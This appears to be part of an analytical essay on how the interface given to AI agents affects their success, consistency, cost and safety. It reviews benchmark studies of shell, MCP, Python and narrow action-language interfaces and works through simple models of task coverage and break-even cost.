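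Members of the same project later released mini-SWE-agent, which is about 100 lines of code and gives the model only a shell. *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?* (Yang, Yu and Desell, 2026) reports that it has solved more than 74% of SWE-bench Verified, a human-checked subset of the same benchmark. This shows that a shell can be enough for a good result, but not, as is sometimes assumed, that custom commands no longer help. The result involves a much stronger model and different problems, and the same model might have done better still with extra commands.

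In *The Devil Is in the Interface*, Xu, Saghir and colleagues (2026) compared six interfaces by running three models on 65 bugs from SWE-bench Live, a version of SWE-bench designed to avoid problems that models saw in training. Each model tried every bug ten times with each interface, for a total of 11,700 runs. One interface was a shell alone. Another added commands for searching, viewing, replacing text and creating files, though the shell could already do all of these.

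The share of bugs that each model fixed was similar with all six interfaces. However, the extra commands made the models more consistent. Xu and colleagues measured this with pass^k, the probability that *k* attempts at the same bug all succeed. If *c* of *n* attempts succeeded, then

pass^k = C(c, k) / C(n, k)

where C(n, k) is the number of ways to choose *k* attempts from *n*. An agent that fixes a bug in eight of its ten attempts has a success rate of 80%, but its pass^5 is only 56/252, or 22%. Someone who relies on an agent to do the same kind of job every day may care more about the second number.

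| Model | pass^9, shell alone | pass^9, extra commands | Change in input tokens |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-Coder 30B | 2.0% | 9.4% | −32% |
| Kimi K2.5 | 26.6% | 28.0% | +20% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 25.2% | 28.3% | +20% |

The paper's headline claim that consistency improved by up to 4.7 times comes from Qwen's result, a gain of only 7.4 percentage points. Qwen, the weakest of the three models, made about three errors per run when it used the shell alone. The extra commands reduced its broken edits from 1.64 per run to 0.19 and its malformed commands from 0.96 to 0.01. Kimi and Sonnet rarely made these errors, so they had less to gain.

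The extra commands made Kimi and Sonnet more expensive to run because the commands split up the work. Sonnet often combined several operations in one shell command, such as finding a file and printing part of it. When each operation had its own tool, Sonnet took more turns, and the harness sent the conversation again each time.

The consistency gains for Qwen and Kimi persisted when Xu and colleagues increased the number of attempts to 30. To see whether the results would be the same for other bugs, they also tested both models on 72 more coding tasks. Averaged over the old and new tasks, pass^5 rose by 9.5 points for Qwen and 2.5 for Kimi.

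### Whether stronger models still need the help

Xu and colleagues' results suggest that hand-made commands now help less than they did with GPT-4 Turbo, but their three models come from different companies. Comparing generations of the same model family is more informative. Hou, Dumitru and colleagues (2026) made this comparison in *MCP vs. CLI* at Scale, a company that tests AI models. They generated a command-line version of every tool on 16 MCP servers from its MCP definition, so an agent could do the same things through either interface.

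The 50 tasks typically needed 50 to 100 tool calls in simulated businesses. With Claude Opus 4.6, the better interface depended on the task. Agents succeeded on about 17.7% of tasks with the command line and 8.5% with MCP in an environment with over 30,000 records, where they had to search widely. In a smaller environment, where tasks called for precise look-ups and updates, they succeeded on about 11.8% with MCP and 7.3% with the command line. With Opus 4.8, the two interfaces performed similarly.

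Hou and colleagues tested GPT-5.4 with and without reasoning, and the results give a hint about the cause. Switching from MCP to the command line reduced the rate of badly constructed queries from 36% to 23% without reasoning, but only from 16% to 10% with it. A better interface can prevent badly constructed queries, but it won't help much when an agent can search correctly but leaves many records unchecked.

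This is fairly good evidence that stronger models depend less on an interface that guards against small mistakes. But Hou and colleagues' tasks were so hard that the newest models solved only about one in seven. (They don't report this figure, but dividing the cost per run by the cost per solved task gives 14% to 16%.) Differences between interfaces might be larger on tasks that the agents can usually finish.

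The benefit of combining many operations in one program may not shrink in the same way. Wang and colleagues found that it grew as models became more capable, because weak models could barely write useful programs. In newer experiments, the benefit shows up more as lower cost than as higher task success.

### Fewer turns and lower bills

Xu and colleagues also tested an interface in which the agent's only tool was Python. Qwen's average run fell from 77 steps with the shell to 46 with Python, Kimi's from 65 to 47 and Sonnet's from 80 to 55, and input tokens also fell. Sonnet wasted less work in Python because it tended to edit and test in the same step, whereas with the shell it often rewrote a file several times before running it.

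The operations were almost the same in both versions, since an agent with a shell can run Python. Xu and colleagues inspected 100 of the Python actions and found that 97 had a direct equivalent in what the shell agents did, while the other three were too broken to interpret. But Python made the weakest model, Qwen, less consistent. Its pass^9 fell from 2.0% to 0.2%, while the two stronger models stayed within two points of their shell results.

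Yang, Yu and Desell gave two commercial agents, Claude Code with Sonnet 4.6 and Codex with GPT-5.5, a single tool called `execute_code` in place of all their usual tools. It runs Python and shell commands and keeps its variables between calls. They compared this setup with each agent's default tools and with a shell plus a few tools for reading files. The agents worked on 93 computing tasks, such as data processing, and 100 bugs from SWE-bench, three times each.

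The table compares `execute_code` with whichever of the other two setups was cheaper.

| Agent and tasks | Change in share solved | Change in cost |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, computing | 0.0 points | −24.6% |
| Codex, computing | +2.5 points | −6.7% (not significant) |
| Claude Code, bugs | −1.7 points | +14.4% (not significant) |
| Codex, bugs | +0.3 points | −19.9% |

None of the changes in the share of tasks solved was statistically significant. An agent with one tool did about as well as one with a full set, but that one tool can do almost everything the others can.

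The savings on Codex came from smaller inputs. It made about 18 calls to the model per bug with either the default tools or `execute_code`, but `execute_code` reduced tool calls from 23 to 17 because one script could do several look-ups. The scripts also returned less unwanted text. In one run with the default tools, a broad keyword search reached the output limit of about 40,000 characters. With `execute_code`, the agent wrote a narrower search that returned 1,514 characters.

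Claude Code had more trouble fixing bugs because it had to write a script for every change to a file, whereas its normal edit tool needs only the old and new text. Its output grew by 40%. Most of the extra cost came from long runs that failed. On the 49 bugs that it usually fixed with all three setups, `execute_code` cost only 4.1% more, a difference that could easily be due to chance.

Codex has no setting to disable its own file-editing tool, so the researchers had to tell the model not to use it. The model made very few direct calls to the tool, but it was still able to use it.

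Hou and colleagues' costs depended heavily on the harness. Opus 4.8 ran in Claude Code, and GPT-5.5 in a harness built with OpenAI's Agents SDK.

| Model | Interface | Turns per run | Median time | Cost per run | Cost per solved task |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.8 | MCP | 16.0 | 423 s | $2.84 | $18.90 |
| Opus 4.8 | Command line | 42.2 | 597 s | $3.52 | $25.10 |
| GPT-5.5 | MCP | 22.0 | 223 s | $3.51 | $25.20 |
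| GPT-5.5 | Command line | 45.2 | 267 s | $2.11 | $12.80 |

The command line took more turns and time than MCP with both models, partly because the agents had to look up how each command worked. Yet it was cheaper for GPT-5.5, whose harness put large MCP results in the conversation and sent them again on every turn. Claude Code saves those results to a file. If GPT-5.5's harness did the same, much of the command line's price advantage might disappear without any change to the tools.

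When agents had both interfaces, the models nearly always used MCP rather than the command line, and the agents didn't gain the strengths of both. Hou and colleagues got better results with some models by offering broad searches only as commands, and precise reads and changes only through MCP.

### When the tools don't cover the task

The result that looks strongest for open access comes from ServiceNow, which sells software for running company operations. *Terminal Agents Suffice for Enterprise Automation* (Bechard, Marquez Ayala and colleagues, 2026) compares three kinds of agent on 729 tasks in ServiceNow's own product, the software development platform GitLab and the business management system ERPNext. One used MCP tools, another used a web browser, and the third had a terminal and a file system, from which it could send its own requests to each platform. The table gives the success rate,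 with the average cost per task in brackets.

| Model | MCP tools | Browser | Terminal |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | 32.9% ($0.51) | 72.2% ($3.29) | 72.7% ($0.56) |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 39.2% ($0.58) | 79.9% ($3.97) | 78.7% ($1.22) |
| GPT-5.4 | 38.8% ($0.23) | 73.4% ($0.43) | 73.5% ($0.19) |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 37.1% ($0.11) | 68.9% ($0.69) | 77.5% ($0.09) |

The terminal succeeded about as often as the browser with three of the four models and clearly more often with Gemini, and it cost much less. On GitLab, however, the browser had the higher success rate with all four models. MCP tools cost little per attempt, but with Sonnet 4.6 they cost about $1.55 per completed task, compared with $0.77 for the terminal.

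The gap of roughly 35 to 40 points between MCP tools and the terminal is far larger than any gap in the experiments above. Bechard and colleagues used the same model with both interfaces, but the operations available to it differed. They used existing open-source MCP servers without adding to them, and many tasks needed an operation that no tool provided. When a user wanted to order an iPad, the MCP agent found it in the catalogue but had no tool for placing an order, so it created a support ticket and failed the task. The terminal agent got several errors from badly formatted requests and wrong addresses, but it tried other requests and completed the order.

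The number of tools did not reliably indicate how much they covered. ServiceNow's server had 83 tools, and agents using them completed only 11.5% to 18.5% of its tasks. ERPNext's server had seven general tools for reading, creating, changing and deleting records of any type, and every model completed at least 55.6% of its tasks with them. These few tools gave agents broad authority, much like the money-transfer language in the first section's table.

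Bechard and colleagues accept that the weakness lies in the tool catalogues they tested, not in MCP itself. Hou and colleagues' results support this, because recent models did about equally well with MCP and a command line when both offered the same operations. Similarly, in Hong and colleagues' medical records test, agents did only slightly worse with typed tools than with raw web requests that covered the same operations. The studies' tasks and models differ too much to combine their results, but the most likely explanation for the failures at ServiceNow is that the MCP agents lacked operations they needed.

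A company could respond by adding an ordering tool or by giving the agent a terminal. The tool would let the agent place orders. The terminal would let it do anything its account can do through the platform's interface, including operations that no task requires. Bechard and colleagues' experiment doesn't compare the two, so its success rates can't establish that a terminal is necessary.

### The missing comparison

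The table shows what each comparison kept the same. Operations count as the same if an agent could do the same things to its environment through either interface, even if one interface required many more steps.

| Comparison | Interfaces | Same model | Same operations | Main result |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Wang and colleagues | Python, JSON, text | Yes | Yes, but Python could also compute | Python ahead on tasks with several tools |
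| Patel and colleagues | Python, JSON | Yes | Yes, but only stubs | Python equal or better for 11 of 14 models |
| Yang, Jimenez and colleagues | Shell, shell with custom commands | Yes | Yes | Custom commands added 7 points |
| SWE-agent and mini-SWE-agent | Custom commands, shell alone | No | Yes | Can't separate the interface from the model |
| Xu and colleagues | Shell, added tools, Python | Yes | Nearly | Similar success, with differences in consistency and cost |
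| Yang, Yu and Desell | Default tools, shell, one code tool | Yes | Nearly | Similar success, with cost changes from −25% to +14% |
| Hou and colleagues | MCP, command line | Yes | Yes | Little difference in success for the newest models |
| Bechard and colleagues | MCP, browser, terminal | Yes | No | MCP far behind |

Most of these experiments compare one form of open access with another. In all the coding studies, the agent could run arbitrary code whichever interface it had. Wang's JSON agents and Hou's MCP agents had fixed lists of tools, but neither had a small language, like the refund language, with its own grammar for combining them. The studies mainly measure success, consistency, time and cost. None was designed to measure how often an agent did something harmful on the way to a correct result.

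An experiment that addressed both gaps could use a job such as airline bookings and give the same model four interfaces:

- typed calls for a fixed set of operations
- a small language that can combine those operations
- Python that can reach only those operations
- a shell with a login to the booking system

Comparing typed calls with Python would show the value of a more expressive language, and testing the small language would show how much of that value a restricted grammar can provide. Comparing Python with the shell would show which tasks need more authority. The researchers would have to write the small language before seeing the test tasks, since otherwise they could add a command for each one. They would also need to count unauthorised changes in every version, including in runs where the agent completed its task.

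## How much work a fixed set of actions can cover

The main argument for open access is that real work needs actions nobody listed in advance. A simple model shows how quickly small gaps in a list could add up. Suppose a narrow interface has the right command for any one step of a task with probability *c*, independently of the other steps. The chance that it has every command an *n*-step task needs is

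cⁿ

With *c* at 0.95, this is 60% for a 10-step task and 36% for a 20-step task. Some real tasks are much longer. *TraceLab* (Zhu, Jacob and colleagues) recorded the coding agents that 43 developers used in their daily work. The median request led to two tool calls, but one in ten led to 30 or more, and one in a hundred to 113 or more.

| Steps in the task | All covered, at 95% per step | All covered, at 99% per step |
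|---|---|---|
| 2 | 90% | 98% |
| 10 | 60% | 90% |
| 20 | 36% | 82% |
| 30 | 21% | 74% |
| 113 | 0.3% | 32% |

### Why the steps aren't independent

In a bounded job, the same few actions recur, and an interface that has `get_ticket` for the first call still has it for the fiftieth. If a 20-step task uses only four different operations, and each has a 95% chance of being on the list, the chance that the list covers the whole task is 0.95⁴, or about 81%.

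Gaps may also cluster in certain requests. If the interface has no commands for 5% of requests and every command for the rest, it covers 95% of tasks, however long they are. But assuming that gaps are independent can also overestimate coverage. If every 20-step task ends with the same missing command, the interface covers 95% of the steps and none of the tasks. The ServiceNow agent that found an iPad in the catalogue but had no tool for ordering it had this kind of gap. A builder measuring an interface's coverage should therefore count the whole tasks it can complete.

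### What coding agents run

By July 2026, SyFI TraceLab, a dataset from University of Washington researchers, had grown to 8,058 sessions from 52 users of Claude Code and Codex. Shell commands made up 423,280 of its 743,819 tool calls, or 56.9%.

One shell command can start several programs. SyFI TraceLab separates them and counts about 1.3 million program runs, involving 1,235 different programs. Seven common ones account for 55.1% of the runs:

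| Program | What it mostly does | Share of runs |
|---|---|---|
| `echo` | Prints text, such as progress labels | 18.1% |
| `grep` | Searches text | 10.1% |
| `sed` | Prints or edits chosen lines | 9.1% |
| `head` | Shows the start of a file | 6.4% |
| `tail` | Shows the end of a file | 4.2% |
| Python scripts | Anything | 4.2% |
| `rg` | Searches text | 3.0% |

Before releasing the data, the researchers listed 351 program names that they could publish without revealing anything private. These were about a third of the 1,044 names in the data at that point, but they accounted for 99.04% of runs. The researchers didn't choose them by frequency, so the 351 most common programs would cover at least as much.

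The average request involved about 15 program runs. If runs were independent, a request of that length would have an 87% chance of using only the listed programs (0.9904¹⁵ ≈ 0.87). The real figure could be higher, because a project's own unusual programs probably turn up in the same requests.

The two agents also used different programs for similar work. Claude Code mostly used `grep`, `head` and `tail` to search and read files, while Codex relied more on `sed` and `rg`. An interface with a few good commands for searching, reading and editing might therefore replace dozens of programs.

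However, a list of 351 programs isn't a narrow language if Python is on it. Removing Python would affect only a small share of runs, but they may be important ones. In *Breaking Down Bash Commands in TraceLab* (Zhu, Jacob and colleagues, 2026), Python accounts for 3.7% of Claude Code's program runs and more than half of its measured running time. (The researchers could time only commands that started a single program, which were about 15% of Claude Code's shell commands.)

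The agents also needed to combine programs. Claude Code used several programs in 84% of its shell commands. A list that allowed only one program per call would rule out these commands even if it included every program.

The dataset comes mainly from researchers building and testing software, and it shows what agents choose when they have a shell. Agents might do the same jobs differently with another interface, so the counts can't establish which programs they need.

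### Why customer service is different

The airline agent serves thousands of customers with the same 14 functions, which cover a short list of jobs, such as finding, booking, changing and cancelling trips.

The benchmark's designers created the tasks to fit these functions, though, which partly explains the agent's coverage. A real airline also gets calls about lost luggage, bereavement and names misspelled on passports. The airline could measure coverage by sampling past requests and checking how many the 14 functions could have completed.

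### Responses to an uncovered request

Suppose a customer wants to exchange a lamp for one in another colour, but the shop's refund language has no `exchange` command. The shop can handle the request in four ways.

| Response | Delay | Labour | Safety |
|---|---|---|---|
| Refuse | None for the agent, but the customer must look elsewhere | None for the shop at first | The language's limits still hold |
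| Pass it to a person | Often minutes, sometimes hours | Staff time for every such request | Depends on the person, whom an attacker may also fool |
| Extend the language after review | The first customer waits for the new command, later ones don't | Developers and reviewers, plus upkeep | Depends on the review |
| Use an escape hatch | Almost none | Little | The agent gains all the authority of the hatch |

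SyFI TraceLab's data gives a rough idea of the delay when an agent needs a person. The median wait for a user's next message was two minutes with Claude Code and one minute with Codex, but the average was about 40 minutes with each, because some users stayed away for hours. Claude Code also has a command, `ExitPlanMode`, that presents a plan for the user's approval. The 672 of these calls with recorded times took about 239 hours in total, or an average of 21 minutes each. Codex's shell commands took about seven seconds each, including later waits for commands that were still running. A support desk with staff on duty should respond faster than a developer who is away from the computer.

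The labour is easier to estimate. If a shop gets 1,000 requests a day and its language misses 5% of them, staff have to deal with 50. At ten minutes each, that is a little over eight hours, or one full-time job. (These figures are invented.)

Extending the language worked well at Ginkgo, where GPT-5 suggested new reagents and staff decided which ones to add. The delay in adding them mattered little because the work ran in rounds over six months. A customer waiting for a lamp is unlikely to wait for a software release, so the shop would also need a way to transfer customers to staff.

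An escape hatch is fast, but it makes every request less safe. If the refund agent has a shell for the 5% of requests that its action language can't handle, planted text can also make it use the shell during the other 95%. The shop could require approval for each use, but that brings back the delay, and approvers may click through without reading.

### Languages that models barely know

Writing a new language to cover a job creates another problem, because the model has seen no programs in it. Giagnorio, Martin-Lopez and Bavota (2026), in *No Resource, No Benchmarks, No Problem?*, tested four older models, including GPT-4o, on 227 hard programming tasks. The models solved 59% to 89% in Python and Java, but at most 1% in Gleam and MoonBit, two recent languages with very little public code.

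Newer models do better when they can look things up and test their work. In *Bridging the Knowledge Void*, Shen, Cheng and colleagues (2026) let a model run code and search the documentation for Cangjie, a programming language released in 2024. In *Compiler-Guided Inference-Time Adaptation*, Li and Krishnamachari (2026) tested GPT-5 on 56 exercises in Idris, a rarely used language with very strict types.

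Two more studies used Brainfuck, which has only eight commands and is deliberately hard to program in. *EsoLang-Bench* (Sharma and Chopra, 2026) had the model write programs directly from the documentation. *Frontier Coding Agents Use Metaprogramming to Adapt to Unfamiliar Programming Languages* (Sharma, Thorat and Chopra, 2026) gave agents the same 80 problems along with files, a shell and unlimited test runs.

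| Language and model | Help | Tasks solved |
|---|---|---|
| Cangjie, Claude Sonnet 4.5 | None | 45% |
| | Repeated documentation searches | 66% |
| | Documentation tools and code execution | 82% |
| Idris, GPT-5 | None | 39% |
| | Official manual | 61% |
| | Up to 20 rounds of compiler and test feedback | 96% |
| Brainfuck, GPT-5.4 | Documentation | 2.5% |
| | Documentation and up to five rounds of feedback | 6.2% |
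| | Files, a shell and unlimited test runs | 98.8% |

Being able to run the code helped at least as much as having documentation. When Shen and colleagues took away Qwen3-Max's ability to run code, its score on the Cangjie tasks fell from 74% to 54%. Removing documentation search had the same effect. Worked examples helped less in most of these tests. Three solved programs raised scores in the esoteric languages by an average of 0.8 percentage points, and *PROBE* (2026) also reports that compiler feedback helped much more than an example. However, *Automating Code Generation for Semiconductor Equipment Control from Developer Utterances with LLMs* (2025) reports significant gains for a semiconductor equipment language from examples arranged from easy to hard.

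The Idris result probably overstates what an agent could do in live use, because GPT-5 could see which tests it had failed and keep trying until it passed them. A refund agent has no test to show that the mug was never broken. GPT-5 spent most of its attempts on compiler errors, and a compiler can't detect a mistake like refunding an unbroken mug either. In *From LLMs to Agents in Programming*, Kjellberg, Staron and Fotrousi (2026) gave 16 models a C compiler. The share of programs that compiled rose by 5.3 to 79.4 percentage points, but the compiler had no effect on what the programs meant.

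The best agents solved the Brainfuck problems by writing Python programs that generated the Brainfuck code, which let them use named variables and reusable functions. When Sharma and colleagues banned these generators, GPT-5.4 fell from 79 solved problems to 29, and Claude Opus 4.6 from 64 to 27. Written advice about the method didn't help weaker agents much. A library of Python helper functions raised Claude Sonnet 4.6 from 12 solved problems to 64, though Claude Haiku 4.5 still solved only seven.

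A builder can use this method without giving the agent more authority. The agent can write Python in a sealed sandbox to generate the program, while the machine accepts only the finished program in the narrow language, much as Ginkgo's laboratory accepted only a plate file. But generated programs may be too long for a person to check. In one case, the program Opus wrote directly had 1,884 characters and failed, while the generated one had 24,500 and passed.

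These languages are also much harder than most action languages need to be. Laboratory agents learned theirs from a description or a manual, and the refund language fits on a few lines. *Utilizing LLMs for Industrial Process Automation* (2025) found that general-purpose models could, with prompting alone, make simple changes to programs in RAPID, the robot language of the equipment maker ABB.

### What it costs to build and maintain

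The builder of a narrow interface has to write its commands, checks, documentation and error messages. TACIT's shared code alone is about ten times as long as all of mini-SWE-agent, which offers only a shell. But lines of code are a poor measure of work, and a shell also needs a sandbox, which mini-SWE-agent's 100 lines don't include.

Training a model on the new language adds an expense that builders can often avoid. Giagnorio and colleagues trained open models on the available Gleam and MoonBit code, then restored their ability to follow instructions by adding the difference in weights between an instruction-following model and its untuned version. This raised scores on the hard tasks to just over 25%. For Cangjie, a small model with special training solved 35% of the code generation tasks, far fewer than Claude Sonnet 4.5 with documentation and code execution. Companies can already rent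 Claude Sonnet 4.5, though the two models differ too much in size for a fair comparison of methods.

Training also goes out of date. MoonBit gained a new kind of package in May 2025, and training on earlier code wouldn't cover it. A company that relies on documentation can update a page instead of retraining the model.

Whether a new command is worth adding depends on how often people need it. If it takes *B* hours to build and *m* hours a month to maintain, and saves staff *t* hours on each of *N* requests a month, the months needed to recover the cost are

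B / (N × t − m)

Suppose a command takes 16 hours to build and two hours a month to maintain, and saves ten minutes per request. With 60 requests a month, it has saved as much time as was spent on it after two months. With 12, maintenance takes as much time as the command saves. A company would therefore add commands for common requests and leave rare ones to staff, even if its developers could foresee them all.

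Some tools also lose their value as models improve. In *How Foundational Models Became Superhuman in Bash* (2026), a developer describes rebuilding his agent's harness every few months to see what he can delete. In the latest version, he removed every tool except a shell and a viewer for images and other media. He says the agent did as well or better on the same coding tasks, but gives no figures. Commands that help a model edit files may become unnecessary, but a check that a customer owns an order remains useful with any model because it enforces a business rule.

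### The case for general agents

General agents are most useful when each request is different and long requests matter. In one of the developer's examples, an agent searches compressed server logs for the web addresses with the most errors. It writes a program that unpacks the logs, loads them into a temporary database, matches requests with errors and returns five records. A tool designer could have anticipated each operation, but probably not this combination.

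Of the 1,044 program names in TraceLab's inventory, 693 together accounted for less than 1% of runs. Adding commands for all of them would be a poor use of developers' time, and new projects would need others. The longest requests are the most likely to need a missing command, and they are also where an agent could save the most work.

However, the log search only needs to read one folder and write temporary files, so this example supports giving the agent a general language, but not a connection to the live system. The same developer recommends that software outside the model control access to files, the network and destructive actions.

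### When one failure costs too much

A narrow interface can cost less overall for a job with a short list of operations and a very expensive worst case. Suppose an open interface would save $10 of staff time on each of the 4% of requests that a narrow one can't handle, or $0.40 per request on average. If the open interface also makes a $1 million accident possible, the average loss exceeds the saving when the accident happens more than once in 2.5 million requests.

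Testing could hardly establish that the accident is rarer than that. With no accidents in *n* independent tests, the 95% upper limit on the rate is about 3/*n*, so the company would need around 7.5 million clean runs. Removing the dangerous command and reviewing the remaining code would be easier, which is why Hong and colleagues favour domain-specific agents for companies with a lot to lose. The review can still miss a bug, as happened with Instagram's account recovery tool, and it covers only the accidents someone has thought of.

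If the worst accident costs $100, the break-even rate is one in 250 requests, and about 750 clean runs would be enough. A company can sometimes keep the worst accident that small by limiting what the agent can reach, for example with a spending cap or a copy of the database, while still letting it write general code.
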